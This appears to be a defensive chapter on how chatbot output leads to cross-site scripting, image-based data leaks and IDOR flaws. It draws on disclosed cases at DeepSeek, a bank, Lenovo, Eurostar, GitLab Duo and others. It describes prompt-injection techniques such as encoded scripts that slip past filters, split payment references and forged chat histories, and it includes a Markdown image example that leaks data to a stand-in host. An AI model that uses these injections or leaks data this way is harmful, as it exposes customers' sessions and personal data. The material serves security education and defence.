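Headings, lists and bold text do not require raw HTML. TanStack, which publishes open-source web libraries, has a Markdown renderer that encodes HTML tags by default and removes link addresses that would run code. It lets the developer decide how to handle remote images and ordinary outbound links.

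Even a well-designed renderer can fail in one small part of its code. AnythingLLM is an application for chatting about a collection of documents. According to NVD's *CVE-2026-41318 Detail*, an entry in the US government's vulnerability database, AnythingLLM's developers ran the sanitiser everywhere they displayed Markdown except in chart captions, which the model writes. The renderer also copied each image's alternative text, a description that stands in for the picture, into the HTML without encoding it. HTML encloses that text in quotation marks, so a quotation mark inside it can end the text early and turn the rest into attributes, including ones that hold code.

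LibreChat, another chat application, had nearly the same fault. According to NVD, the developers had written their own rule for images, which checked whether the address was safe. If it was, their code passed the image to a library's standard renderer, which did not encode quotation marks in the description. The dangerous text was in the description, which the rule did not check. The script ran inside a preview frame, which may have limited the damage.

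*CVE-2026-70492* (2026), from OSV's public database of flaws in open-source software, describes how Open WebUI mishandled errors when displaying mathematical formulas. If a formula crashed the typesetting library in a particular way, the application inserted the formula's source into the page as HTML, when plain text would have sufficed. A script hidden in the formula could steal the session token of anyone who viewed the message.

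The flaw in New API, a gateway through which organisations manage their use of models, didn't require such a corner case. OSV's *CVE-2026-25802* (2026) reports that a script could run whenever the model's output contained a script tag. The developers of all four products have released fixes. An advisory establishes that a flaw existed, but not that anybody exploited it, and none of these products is a typical shop widget. But a shop's developers use the same kinds of parser and renderer, and can make the same mistakes in a caption or an error message.

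### Why input filters miss the markup

Many sites try to stop XSS by rejecting input that contains suspicious tags. This was never a complete defence, and a model weakens it further because the attacker no longer has to submit any markup. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian point out that a model may generate markup from a description, decode it, transform it, or preserve it from the input. An input filter has a good chance of catching the markup only when the model preserves it from the input.

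The security researcher Johann Rehberger came across the first possibility in 2024, when he asked DeepSeek's chatbot for a list of the strings that testers use to look for XSS. He had typed no markup himself, but one of the strings ran in his browser as the answer appeared. An attack on his own account was of little interest, so he then looked for a way to use this against another user, as Embrace The Red's *DeepSeek AI* recounts.

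Rehberger wrote a text file of the kind someone might upload for analysis. It contained an encoded script and an instruction to decode it and output only the result. The model output the decoded script, and the page ran it. The script displayed the session token that DeepSeek's site kept in browser storage, which was all an attacker needed to take over the account. The demonstration did not send the token anywhere, though Rehberger thought that would be easy to add. DeepSeek fixed the flaw about a day after he reported it.

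He had encoded the script because plain markup tends to set off firewalls and makes many models refuse. The encoded version contained no tags for a filter to detect, and the model produced the dangerous string after the input had passed the filter.

In July 2026, Positive Security reported that it had found a similar flaw in its own bank's chatbot in under two minutes. The chatbot could add payees, so a tester asked it to add one whose name was an image tag. A broken image appeared in the answer, so the page was treating the model's output as HTML. Some safeguard blocked the best-known test for whether a script would run, but a less familiar variant got through.

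So far the tester could attack only himself. To reach another customer, the team used the reference text of a bank transfer. This field holds 140 characters and forbids angle brackets, so it could hardly carry XSS into a conventional banking page. The team replaced the forbidden characters with stand-ins and split the attack text between two one-cent transfers. When the chatbot read the transactions, the model joined the parts and restored the characters.

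According to Positive Security, a customer can trigger the attack just by asking for the month's transactions. In its recorded demonstration, however, the user's own prompt repeated some of the instructions, because the team was reluctant to send many test transfers through a live bank. A second demonstration was closer to a realistic attack. The team put the script in an invoice as white text on a white background, and the user only had to upload the invoice and ask the chatbot to add the payee.

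The bank at first thought the flaw could harm only the user who typed the prompt. It released a fix within about three hours of acknowledging the report, and the chatbot's answers then appeared to be fully encoded. The fix works whatever the payment reference contains, because it applies after the model has written its answer.

### What streaming does to sanitising

Most widgets display an answer piece by piece as the model writes it, so that the customer does not have to wait for the whole answer. A piece can end anywhere, including the middle of a tag. Suppose `<b>tent</b>` arrives as `<`, then `b>te`, then `nt</b>`. A sanitiser that checks each piece separately never finds a complete opening tag, but the browser receives one if the widget joins the pieces and inserts them as HTML.

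Chrome for Developers therefore advises sanitising the combined output. Each time a piece arrives, the widget should check everything received so far. If the sanitiser removes anything, the widget should stop displaying the answer, because a cleaned-up answer is no longer what the model wrote. This would annoy users of a programming assistant, which has good reason to mention HTML tags, but it would do little harm to a shop that sells tents.

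Checking and redrawing the whole answer each time a new piece arrives is slow, so developers have a reason to process only the new text. Streaming parsers make this practical. When such a parser receives a single asterisk, which could begin a list item, italics or bold text, it waits for more text until the meaning is clear. Shopify, which hosts online shops, uses a processor that reads one character at a time and holds back anything resembling Markdown until the element is complete. This solves a display problem, but the widget still has to check whether the completed element is safe.

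The order of the steps also matters. In Chrome's sample code, the sanitiser examines the answer while it is still Markdown, and a separate parser then builds the page elements. A parser can create elements, such as links, that were not written as HTML in the text, so the developer also relies on the parser to refuse dangerous addresses. Sanitising after the conversion covers these elements but leaves a smaller gap, because the sanitiser parses the HTML and returns a cleaned string, which the browser then parses again. web.dev's *Safe DOM manipulation with the Sanitizer API* warns that the second parse can differ from the first and gives this as a reason to build sanitising into the browser.

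### Reflected, stored and DOM-based XSS

Security engineers distinguish forms of XSS by how the script reaches the page. In reflected XSS, the site returns the script in its response to the request that carried it. In stored XSS, the site saves the script and displays it later, often to someone else. In DOM-based XSS, the page's own code inserts unsafe text into the document tree.

Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian class the DeepSeek case as reflected XSS because the answer appeared immediately in the chat that prompted it. The same answer would become stored XSS if the application saved it in a support ticket, comment or chat history and later showed it to another user without sanitising it.

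A planted review on Tarnside's site fits neither description exactly. The database stores the attacker's instruction, but the instruction may be ordinary English, in which case a moderator who scanned the stored reviews for tags would find nothing. The script doesn't exist until the model answers Maya. Singh and colleagues point out this difference between a payload that the attacker injects directly and one that the model produces.

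The model also makes the attack less predictable. PortSwigger's *Lab*, an exercise in which students attack a practice store through its live chat, warns that the chat may respond differently each time and that students may have to rephrase their prompts. But the model has to produce the markup only once. After the markup is saved in Tarnside's transcript, it is a fixed string that will take effect whenever somebody opens the transcript in a console that inserts it as HTML.

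DOM-based XSS overlaps with the reflected and stored forms. Chat widgets commonly receive the answer as data and add it to the page with a script, so a reflected or stored attack on a chatbot is often DOM-based as well. NVD calls the AnythingLLM flaw "stored DOM-level XSS" because the server keeps the chat history and the chat page's code turns it into elements in every other user's browser. A security scanner that examines only the HTML pages a server sends could miss such a flaw.

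Some stored attacks on chatbots bypass the model. WPBot is a support chatbot plugin for WordPress, and Wordfence's *WPBot &lt;= 8.4.9* (2026) describes how anyone without an account could save a conversation containing a script, which then ran whenever a user opened the affected page. The plugin required a token with each request to save a conversation, but it printed that token on every public page of the site. Its makers fixed this in version 8.5.0. The mistake resembles the one behind forged conversation histories, since the server accepted a visitor's version of the conversation without sufficient checks.

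Open WebUI had a related flaw. According to *CVE-2026-26193* (2026), a user could edit a saved chat so that one of the chatbot's replies contained an embedded frame with permission to run scripts. The user could then send the script to other people on the same installation by sharing a link to the chat.

Flowise, a tool for building chatbots, has had both kinds of problem. Miggo's *CVE-2024-9148* traces an earlier flaw to the widget that customers embed in their own sites, which inserted parsed Markdown through `innerHTML` without sanitising it. A later entry, OSV's *CVE-2025-71331* (2026), covers scripts that arrived in a chat message or in content that a custom function fetched from an outside website.

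### Images that carry data out

Suppose Tarnside now encodes every HTML tag in the model's answers but still displays Markdown images, because customers like to see the tents. No script can run, but an attacker may still be able to read part of Maya's conversation.

In Markdown, an image consists of a description and an address:

`![tent](https://pictures.example/dot.png?note=marmalade)`

When the widget adds this image to the page, the browser requests the address without Maya clicking anything. The image can be a single transparent dot. The request includes the text after the question mark (the query string), so whoever runs `pictures.example` can find "marmalade" in the server's log. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) makes the general point that an address can contain information besides a destination. If a planted review tells the model to replace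 "marmalade" with the customer's delivery address, the attacker receives that instead.

The same-origin rule does not prevent this, because it has always let web pages load pictures from elsewhere.

The leak has a narrower reach than a script because the model can put into the address only what is in its context. In Tarnside's case, the exposure looks like this:

| Data | When an image request exposes it |
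|---|---|
| Maya's network address, browser type and the time she read the answer | Whenever the browser fetches the image from the attacker's server |
| Her messages and the chatbot's earlier answers | If the model copies them into the address |
| Her order record, including the delivery address | If the lookup tool has run and the model copies the result |
| The system prompt | If the model copies it into the address |
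| Her session cookie for Tarnside | Only if a tool has returned it to the model by mistake, since the browser does not send it to another site |

The attack first needs the model to write an image with the attacker's address, as instructed, and to fill in the data. *A Safety and Security Framework for Real-World Agentic Systems* (2025) scores these two steps separately. Its attack on a report-writing agent supplied an image address with a blank for the user's email, and an answer that included the image but left the blank empty earned half marks. The agent wrote the image into its report with a test email address filled in. The data leaves only if the widget then displays the image and the browser is allowed to fetch it.

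A site can restrict that last step with a Content Security Policy (CSP), a header that specifies which scripts, images and connections the browser should allow. In Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, Rehberger recalls that he reported the image leak to OpenAI and Microsoft in 2023, and that Microsoft used a CSP to block most images in Bing Chat that May. OpenAI took longer. In *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, a note on his programming blog, Simon Willison (2023) reported that ChatGPT had begun to check whether an image was safe before displaying it, and found it odd that OpenAI had not simply blocked images from other sites.

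An allowlist helps only if outsiders cannot use the permitted sites to collect data. The email application Superhuman allowed images from a Google domain that also hosts Google Forms. Willison (2026) explains that a malicious email could make Superhuman's assistant put the contents of other messages into an image address on that domain. When the browser requested the image, it would submit those contents to the attacker's form. Superhuman has fixed the flaw. In EchoLeak, an attack on Microsoft's Copilot, the image address pointed to a permitted Microsoft service that fetches link previews. According to *The Anatomy of a Prompt Injection* (2026), Microsoft's server then passed the request on to the attacker.

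A sanitiser may not stop the leak either, because an image is a legitimate part of a page. GitLab, a site where programmers store and review code, has an assistant called Duo. Legit Security's *Remote Prompt Injection in GitLab Duo Leads to Source Code Theft* showed that a hidden comment could make Duo reveal private code. According to TechRepublic, Duo passed its answers through a well-known sanitiser that left image and form tags in place. The injected instruction told Duo to encode the private code and put it in an image address, which the victim's browser requested when the answer appeared. GitLab has patched the flaw. Duo also displayed its answers as it wrote them. A widget that does this cannot safely postpone its checks until the answer is complete, because the browser may already have sent the request.

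If a store also answers customers through messaging apps, an ordinary link in the chatbot's reply can leak data as automatically as an image does. PromptArmor, a security company, points out that apps such as Telegram and Slack generate previews for links, which involves the same kind of request as a click. Without previews, the attacker has to persuade the customer to click the link.

### Links and images in ChatGPT's page summaries

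*ChatGPhish*, published by the security company Permiso in May 2026, applied these ideas to a current product. The researchers added instructions to web pages and then asked ChatGPT to summarise the pages through a feature in the Firefox browser. ChatGPT wrote a genuine summary, followed by a false notice that somebody had added a new device to the user's account. The notice contained a working link to an address the researchers had chosen, and nothing showed that the link came from the page. The instructions reached ChatGPT through Firefox, but Permiso does not regard the flaw as a browser bug.

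The same method worked with images. In one version, ChatGPT displayed a QR code from the researchers' storage. The code would take anyone who scanned it to a site whose address had never appeared on screen. Scanning it with a phone would also bypass the desktop browser's protections, such as a password manager that won't fill in a login form on an unfamiliar site. In another version, the image was used only to record the visit. The researchers' server received the user's network address, browser type and the time of the answer, along with the referring page if the browser supplied it.

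That is less serious than the leaks from Superhuman or GitLab. Permiso did not show ChatGPT putting private conversation data into an image address. Its first report to OpenAI had XSS in the title, but the published account does not demonstrate any. OpenAI's safeguards may explain the difference. OpenAI describes a check for information from the conversation being sent to a third party. An address copied unchanged from a web page contains no such information, so this kind of check could allow it while still blocking the more serious leak.

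OpenAI first replied that it could not reproduce the problem. After Permiso sent more detail, OpenAI classified the report as not applicable and later as a duplicate of an earlier one. Permiso's timeline ends with publication and records no fix.

A store should take the false notice at least as seriously as the recorded visit. If a planted review made Tarnside's chatbot tell Maya to confirm her password, with a link to a copy of the login page, the message would appear in the store's own widget, next to a correct answer about her tent. Encoding the HTML would not prevent this attack, which requires only a sentence and a link.

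## How the script reaches a shopper, a support agent or an administrator

If an attacker gets Tarnside's chatbot to write a script into his own chat, the script runs in his own browser, under his own account. He gains nothing, since he could run the same code from his browser's developer tools. Security engineers call this self-XSS, and companies often give it a low priority, as the bank in Positive Security's report did at first.

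To do harm, the script has to run in the browser of someone with access the attacker lacks. The attacker could try to persuade a customer to paste the prompt into her own chat, but most customers would find that request odd. Researchers have found several routes that require much less from the victim. The damage each route can cause depends on what the script can do once it reaches the victim's browser.

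### Copying a session or acting within it

Attackers traditionally use XSS to copy the victim's session cookie. The script sends the cookie to the attacker's server, and the attacker puts its value into his own browser. The site then treats him as the victim, without asking for a password. PortSwigger's *Exploiting cross-site scripting vulnerabilities* lists several reasons this can fail. The victim may not be logged in, or the session may expire before the attacker gets to it. The site may tie the session to other details, such as the victim's network address. Many sites also set the HttpOnly flag on the cookie, which hides it from scripts but still lets the browser send it. DeepSeek's site had kept its token in browser storage, which has no such flag.

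A script can use a shopper's session from inside the page without reading the cookie, so HttpOnly does not stop it. Suppose a script runs in the chat widget while Maya is logged in to Tarnside. The script requests her account page, and the browser attaches her cookie. Because the script and the account page share an origin, the script can read the reply. It can then submit the form that changes her email address. If the server accepts the change, the attacker can request a password reset and receive the link at his own address.

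Sites protect such forms against CSRF with a token, a random value that the site puts in its page and expects back with the form. A malicious site in another tab can make Maya's browser send a request, but it cannot read the token. *CSRF and Same-Origin XSS* points out that a script in the site's own page can read it, so a script in Tarnside's page can send requests that look just like Maya's. Y-Security's *Cross Site Request Forgery Prevention Cheat Sheet*, a copy of OWASP's guidance, warns that XSS can defeat every CSRF defense. Sites still need the tokens to stop attackers who have no script on the page.

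The two methods run into different obstacles:

| Obstacle | If the attacker copies the cookie | If the script acts within the session |
|---|---|---|
| The cookie has the HttpOnly flag | The script cannot read it | No effect, since the browser still attaches the cookie |
| The site ties the session to a network address | The site may reject the attacker's browser | No effect, since the requests come from the victim's browser |
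| The form needs an anti-CSRF token | The attacker opens the form himself and receives a valid token | The script reads the token from the page |
| The victim closes the page | The copy works until the session ends | The script stops |
| The site asks for a password or a one-time code before a change | The attacker needs the password or code | The script needs it too, but can ask the victim for it inside the real page |

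With either method, the attacker gets at most the access his victim has on that site. Maya's session gives him one customer's orders and address, while a staff member's session may give him every customer's.

### Hand-off to a support agent

Support agents routinely open chats with strangers, so an attacker can get an agent to see his text by asking for a human. If the agent's console inserts the chatbot's earlier answers as HTML, a script in them will run with the agent's access, which at Tarnside includes issuing refunds and changing email addresses.

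Researchers at Cybernews, a security news site, found a flaw of this kind in Lena, the customer service chatbot on the website of the computer maker Lenovo. Cybernews' *Lenovo “Lena” AI Chatbot Exploited via XSS Prompt Injection* (2025) describes an attack that used a single 400-character prompt. The prompt began with an ordinary question about a laptop's specifications, followed by instructions to give the answer in several formats, including HTML, in the order that Lenovo's server expected. The HTML contained an image whose address did not exist. When the image failed to load, code attached to it sent the browser's cookies to a server the attacker controlled.

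So far the attacker has stolen only his own cookies. But Lenovo's server saved the answer in the conversation history, and the code ran again whenever a browser loaded that history. An attacker could therefore ask for a human agent and wait for the agent to open the chat. "Once you're transferred to a real agent, you're getting their session cookies as well," the researchers said.

After the model wrote the HTML, the attack still depended on several failures in ordinary software. The server stored the answer without sanitizing it, the agent's console displayed it as HTML, and scripts could read the cookies. Fixing only the cookie access would have prevented the theft of cookies, but the script would still have run in the console with the agent's access. Cybernews notes that a script there could change what the agent sees, record keystrokes or send the agent to a fake login page.

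It is less clear how far the researchers went. They state that the transfer yields the agent's cookies, but say only that an attacker "could" or "might" then log in as the agent and read other customers' chats. They also suggest that an attacker might run system commands and move on to other computers in Lenovo's network, but say they attempted none of this. This is the most speculative part of the report, because browsers confine a page's scripts to the page, and an attacker would need a further flaw or a deceived employee to run commands on the agent's computer. News reports nevertheless emphasized the possibility. ITPro warned in the full headline of *Flaw in Lenovo’s customer service AI chatbot* that hackers could "breach networks".

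According to ITPro, the researchers found and reported the flaw on 22 July 2025. Lenovo acknowledged the report on 6 August and had mitigated the flaw by 18 August. In a statement to Cybernews, the company confirmed that its chatbot had an XSS vulnerability and thanked the researchers for letting it deploy a solution "without putting our customers at risk". It neither confirmed nor disputed in the statement that an agent's cookies could leak.

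A month later Cybernews reported much the same flaw at Yellow.ai, a company that supplies chatbots to other businesses. Willing (2025), in *Yellow.ai’s Own Chatbot Got Tricked Into Generating Malicious Code, Reports*, lists Sony, Hyundai, Domino's and Logitech among its clients. According to Daily Security Review's *Security Flaw in Yellow.ai Chatbot Allowed Cookie Theft and Account Hijacking*, the chatbot again answered in HTML, the server saved the answer, and a support agent's browser ran the code when the agent opened the chat. Cybernews called this reflected XSS, but it better fits the usual definition of stored XSS, because the server saved the answer and the agent opened it later.

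Yellow.ai did not acknowledge the report, but it changed the chatbot to display generated code as plain text. After Willing's article appeared, the company said that the researchers had attacked an experimental demo widget on its corporate website and that its production systems have different security settings. SC Media's *Yellow.ai chatbot vulnerability puts cookies at risk*, by contrast, describes the affected chatbot as one that Sony, Domino's and Hyundai use. Cybernews had left open whether clients' chatbots shared the flaw.

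The company's reply also affects how serious the original finding was. If the demo widget had no support desk with customer data behind it, an agent's cookie from that system would have been of little use to an attacker. A client can run the bold-tag test on its own installation, in both the chat window and the agent's console.

A hand-off can also expose an agent to a script that no model wrote. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-8349* (2025), an advisory from Spain's national cybersecurity institute, describes a flaw in Tawk Live Chat that let an attacker upload a PDF containing a script through the chatbot. The application stored the file and displayed it to other users without properly sanitising it. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-11952* (2025) describes a flaw in Oct8ne's chatbot that let an attacker inject a script while creating a transcript for the system to email. INCIBE rates both flaws as medium, at 5.3 on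 a ten-point scale, and warns that either could allow cookie theft or actions in the victim's name. Even if a store carefully encodes its model's answers, an attachment or emailed transcript can still expose its staff.

### A conversation that somebody else opens

The security company Quarkslab reached an administrator's account through a chatbot on a client's production system. The client had hired Quarkslab for a red team exercise, in which specialists attack a system much as a real intruder would. To protect the client, Quarkslab used a mock-up to publish the flaws, an invented medical assistant called FailMed AI that lets patients ask about their own records.

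The team started with an ordinary account with few privileges. The application did not limit the number of prompts, so the team could run Spikee, a tool that sends a prepared set of attack prompts, and check the answers for anything odd. In one answer, the chatbot displayed an image because the prompt had told it to. An attacker could have used this to leak a summary of a patient's medical data in an image address, but would first have had to persuade the patient to enter the prompt. The team kept looking for something with more impact and found that the model would also reproduce an HTML frame with a script in its address. The page ran the script, and the site had no adequate CSP to prevent this.

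This was still self-XSS. It became an account takeover because of two mistakes in the ordinary web code.

The site's session cookie held a JSON Web Token (JWT), a signed statement of who the user is and when the login expires. The site had set none of the usual protective flags on the cookie. The HttpOnly flag would have kept a script on the site's own pages from reading it. Secure and SameSite would not have, because they control when the browser sends a cookie. The sample token that Quarkslab published from its mock-up was valid for eight hours. If a server checks only a token's signature and expiry time, a stolen copy works until it expires, even if the victim logs out.

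The other mistake was an IDOR. The application had no button for sharing a chat, but each chat had a predictable address containing an identifier. The server returned the chat to any logged-in user who supplied that identifier, without checking who owned the chat. An attacker would normally exploit such a flaw to read other people's chats, which is serious in a medical application. Quarkslab instead used it to let a victim open the attacker's chat.

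The attacker gets the chatbot to write the script into one of his own conversations, then sends an administrator a link to that conversation with a plausible reason to open it. When the administrator opens the link while logged in, the page displays the conversation and runs the script, which sends the administrator's token to the attacker's server. The attacker puts the token in his own browser and has full control of the platform.

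Quarkslab considered each flaw modest on its own. The three flaws were a script that affects only its author, a cookie missing a security flag, and a chat that a stranger can open by guessing its number. A company that rates each flaw separately could easily leave all three unfixed for months.

Fixing the IDOR would have closed this route to the administrator, but possibly not every route. Administrators often have legitimate reasons to read users' conversations, for example when a filter has flagged one, and an ownership check would have to let them through. The script would then run just as it did at Lenovo. This may be why Quarkslab mainly advised the client to validate and encode the model's answers when displaying them, and recommended access checks and a strict CSP as further hardening.

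The claim in this case, that an attack on a live system yielded an administrator's session, is the strongest of all the cases here and the hardest for outsiders to check. The client is anonymous and has not replied publicly. Quarkslab's screenshots come from the mock-up, which uses a custom model because the original is no longer available. The report also does not describe who opened the link or whether that person knew about the exercise. The web flaws need no special assumptions, though, and Open WebUI had a flaw, which its developers have since fixed, that offered much the same route through its official chat-sharing feature.

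### Hostile text in the victim's own records

Quarkslab's attack required an administrator to open a link from someone else. Positive Security attacked its own bank's chatbot without a link, by putting the text in the references of two one-cent transfers, which the chatbot later read. An attacker needs only the victim's account number to make such a transfer, and most businesses print theirs on their invoices.

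The script used the customer's session without copying a cookie. The image element in the chatbot's answer fetched a second script from the researchers' server, so the payment references had to hold only a short piece of code, and the second script could be any length. The second script sent a request to the bank's API. Because the request came from the customer's open session, the bank's server returned the customer's email address, which the script sent to the researchers. A CSP could have blocked the outside script, but the bank had none that did.

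Positive Security stopped at the email address. It thought the only remaining barrier to emptying the account was multi-factor authentication, in which the bank asks for a second proof of identity, such as a code from the customer's phone. It didn't try to move any money, so it did not test how much that barrier would have prevented. A bank that asks for a code before every payment to a new payee would stop a script from paying anyone silently. The script could still read whatever the customer could, and it could alter the page so that she approved a payment she did not intend, though this would be harder if the message with the code named the payee and the amount.

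The invoice version is better evidence than the payment route that an outsider could attack a customer who did nothing unusual, because the user's own prompt helped the attack only in the payment demonstration. The researchers ran all the tests on their own business account.

An attacker might also have reached the bank's staff through its chatbot. During the tests, the chatbot automatically forwarded one of the researchers' conversations to a human agent. If the agent's software displayed the answers as HTML, the script would have run there too. The researchers could not see that software and did not test the idea. This kind of attack is called blind XSS, because the attacker learns that his script has run only if it contacts his server. The bank also advertised AI agents that continuously analyse customers' transactions. These might have flagged the strange payment references or followed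 the instructions in them, but Positive Security did not test this either.

A store's records can have the same weakness. If Tarnside let customers send each other gifts, a stranger could use the gift message to put text into Maya's order history. A planted review would reach her chatbot similarly, but from a product page instead of her own records.

### Eurostar's chatbot and a chain that stopped short

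The train operator Eurostar had a chatbot with faults similar to those in the chatbot of Quarkslab's client. Eurostar's chatbot displayed the model's HTML without sanitising it, and its server did not properly check conversation identifiers. Nobody has shown that an attacker could combine the two faults.

Ross Donald of the security firm Pen Test Partners tested Eurostar's chatbot in 2025 under the company's public policy for reporting vulnerabilities. Willing (2025) quotes his findings at length in *Eurostar’s Chatbot Goes Off the Rails, Security Firm Finds*. The customer's browser sent the whole conversation with every question, and a filter signed each message it approved. But the server checked the signature on only the newest message, so Donald could send a harmless question and rewrite the earlier messages. He used this method to get past the filter and extract the system prompt. It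 is a variant of the forged history that Kaya and colleagues found in chatbot plugins.

Eurostar had told the model to answer in HTML so that its answers could link to help articles, and the chat window displayed any HTML the model returned. Donald got the model to return HTML he had chosen. He used only harmless examples, which appeared only in his own chat.

An attacker might have been able to reach other customers through the conversation identifiers. Eurostar's chatbot normally used long, standard identifiers for conversations and messages, but the server also accepted simple strings that Donald made up. He called this "a clear path to a more serious stored or shared XSS", in which one user's script appears in another user's chat. He did not carry out the full attack. Pen Test Partners confirms in City AM's *Eurostar’s new AI chatbot left customers exposed* that it did not try to reach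 other people's conversations or personal data.

Accepting a made-up identifier is a less serious flaw than returning a stranger's conversation, which the server of Quarkslab's client did. For Donald's path to work, Eurostar's server would have had to save the attacker's message under the identifier he chose, and the victim's browser would then have had to use the same identifier and receive the saved message. The last step is doubtful because the browser sent the chat history with each question, and the server may never have sent an old conversation back. Until somebody demonstrates these steps, the finding amounts to self-XSS and a poor check on identifiers.

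Eurostar told City AM that the chatbot was an experimental service without access to other systems, and that no sensitive customer data was at risk because all of it is protected by a customer login. This is a good answer to the worry that the model might reveal somebody's booking, but a less complete one to the danger of a script, which uses the session of the person whose browser runs it. If that person has already logged in, the login doesn't stop the script. Its access to their bookings would have depended on whether the chat window shared an origin with the account pages.

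Eurostar's flaws took far longer to fix than the bank's or Lenovo's. Pen Test Partners first reported them on 11 June 2025 and wrote again a week later, but got no reply. After almost a month, a colleague of Donald's contacted Eurostar's head of security on LinkedIn. Eurostar had meanwhile outsourced its reporting system and had no record of the first report. At one point it suggested that the researchers were attempting blackmail. According to Willing, Pen Test Partners confirmed that Eurostar had fixed the flaws before the researchers published their account in December, although Donald is also quoted as unsure that every fix was complete.

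### Whether criminals have used these flaws

Neither the researchers nor the companies have reported criminal use of the flaws at Lenovo, Yellow.ai, Quarkslab's client, the bank or Eurostar, but this is only weak evidence that nobody used them. CPO Magazine said it was unclear whether malicious hackers had exploited the Lenovo flaw before the researchers disclosed it, and Lenovo's statement does not mention searching its logs.

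Such a search might have found nothing even after a real attack. When a script acts within a support agent's session, its requests come from the agent's usual computer and carry the agent's cookie, so in a log they look like the agent's normal work. A copied cookie is easier to detect because the same session appears at a second network address. If the company kept the transcript, it may also still contain the script, which someone could find by looking for tags in the chatbot's answers.

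Criminals have attacked companies through AI chatbots by simpler means. Positive Security says that in some cases an attacker may simply be able to ask the chatbot to send a reset link for somebody else's password to an email address he names. As an example, it links to a June 2026 report by the security journalist Brian Krebs that hackers had used Meta's AI support bot to seize Instagram accounts. In September 2025, Willing mentioned an FBI warning about criminal groups that were targeting companies' Salesforce systems, which hold customer records, through software connections to a third-party AI chatbot.

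According to these accounts, neither attack needed a script in a victim's browser. This may partly explain why confirmed criminal cases of chatbot XSS are hard to find. An attacker who can get a password-reset link by asking for it has little reason to plant a script and wait for a support agent to open the chat.

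## Attacks through the chatbot's tools and the store's servers

The model's output can also go into Tarnside's own systems, as the argument of a tool call, a database query or the address of a web request. The server acts on it at once, with its own permissions, whereas an attack through the browser has to wait for somebody to open a page. The attacker can often read the result in his own chat window.

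Knowing which tools the model has helps the attacker. Veli Oguzcan Akdag tested a live support chatbot that revealed its system prompt and the descriptions of its internal tools to a visitor who had not logged in. He presented the result at the DEF CON 34 security conference in *From Recon to Full System Prompt Exfiltration*. Often the attacker can guess what tools are available, because nearly every shop's support chatbot can look up orders.

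### An order lookup without an ownership check

Suppose Tarnside's developers gave the lookup function its own database account, which can read every order. Maya's order is number 10482. Another customer, logged in to his own account, types, "Where is order 10482 going?"

1. The server adds the question to the context, correctly labeled as a user message.
2. The model writes `{"tool": "lookup_order", "order_id": "10482"}`.
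3. The server confirms that the tool exists and that the number has the right format, then runs the function.
4. The function sends the database a parameterised query, `SELECT * FROM orders WHERE order_id = ?`, with 10482 in the gap.
5. The database returns Maya's record, and the model writes her delivery address into its answer.

The model answered an ordinary question without any injected instructions, the tool call was well formed, and the query was safe against SQL injection. The query lacks only a second condition, `AND customer_id = ?`, which the server would fill from the session. With that condition, the database would have found no matching order.

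Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian recount a public case that Sumit Shah described in November 2025. A company's chatbot took the order number from a visitor's message and passed it to a lookup function that did not check whether the visitor had logged in or owned the order. Shah asked for the contact details on an order and received another customer's email address. He obtained street addresses with further questions and could ask about several orders in one message.

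The order numbers had a fixed prefix followed by six digits, so there were at most a million, and the chatbot did not limit how quickly a visitor could try them. The title of Shah's post mentions thousands of customer records, although the details Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian give show only that an attacker could have collected that many. They call Shah's questions prompt injection, but the example they print could have come from a customer asking about her own order, so a filter that looks for hostile instructions would have little to detect.

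An advisory from the security company Tenable (2026) reports the same kind of flaw in Chat AI, a chatbot that Yuma AI supplies to several online shops. Anyone could get a customer's shipping address and a list of their purchases by giving an order number or the customer's email address. The advisory lists no known solution. Lookup by email makes it easier for a stalker or former partner to find a customer, because they may already know the customer's email address and would not have to guess an order number.

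A chatbot can resist prompt injection well and still disclose customer data. In Black Lantern Security's *Artificial Foolishness*, a tester describes trying repeatedly to push a client's public chatbot outside its limits and failing every time. The chatbot then offered to show the first 100 entries in a table. The tester accepted, and it returned 100 rows of real customer data. The client took the chatbot offline the same day.

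The ownership check also has to cover requests that bypass the model. ian.sh's *Would you like an IDOR with that?* describes a hiring chatbot that McDonald's used. While looking at their own test application, the researchers noticed a request that fetched an applicant's details by number. They lowered the number and received somebody else's name and contact details, without involving the model. If Tarnside put the ownership check only in the chatbot's tool, a similar request behind the order page could still return Maya's record.

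### Customers who write by email

In the chat widget, the server can take the customer's identity from the session. A chatbot that answers email has no session, so it has to work out the customer from the message. Ayoub and De Ceukelaire (2026), in *Hacking AI customer service agents*, describe what can go wrong. Their article, for the bug bounty company Intigriti, summarises a talk that Inti De Ceukelaire gave at DEF CON 34. (In a bug bounty, a company pays outsiders who report flaws to it.)

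The article's mildest example involves chat transcripts. Many chatbots will email a visitor a copy of the conversation. If an attacker can get that copy sent to someone else, the recipient gets a message from the store's real support address containing text the attacker chose. The article says most security teams would consider this too minor to need quick attention.

One chatbot also let customers continue the conversation by email but did not properly verify the sender. The researchers could forge a victim's address to write to the chatbot as the victim, and they used this to make the support address send the victim a phishing email. If such a chatbot can also edit profiles or read bills, a forged email can trigger those tool calls on the victim's account. The reply would normally go to the victim, but in some cases the researchers could have a copy sent to themselves.

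Email has authentication checks intended to prevent forgery, but they only work if the chatbot uses the address that the mail system checked. One email can contain several sender addresses. In an attack that Ayoub and De Ceukelaire describe, the mail system verified an address that belonged to the attacker, and the chatbot then used a different address in the message to choose the account.

They also describe a way to obtain an authentic email from the victim. The attacker emails someone who is on holiday, making the support desk appear to be the sender and putting an instruction in the subject line. The victim's out-of-office reply then goes to the chatbot with that subject line. The reply comes from the victim's account, but she didn't write the instruction. A session cookie likewise identifies the account but not who wrote the instruction.

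An attacker can sometimes use his own identity and hide a victim's inside a tool's argument. The email standard allows comments within an address, and mail software ignores them. One company's system copied the customer's whole address into the URL of an internal request without encoding it, so the web server read part of the comment as another `email` parameter and returned the victim's profile. Standard URL encoding would have kept the address as a single value.

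In another case, the system used an offer number as part of a file path. The researchers uploaded a data file in place of a profile picture, then supplied an "offer number" that pointed to it. The chatbot read a discount code from their file as though the shop had issued it. The text reached the model as the result of a genuine tool call, so even a correct tool label would not have shown that an outsider wrote it.

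An email can also contain a forged approval. Some support consoles treat quoted lines in an email as earlier messages in the conversation, so an attacker can type a quotation in which the support desk appears to approve his refund. In the article's example, the console displayed the quotation as an operator's message, and the agent went ahead with a $4,200 refund. This is the email version of the forged chat history that Kaya and colleagues found in plugins.

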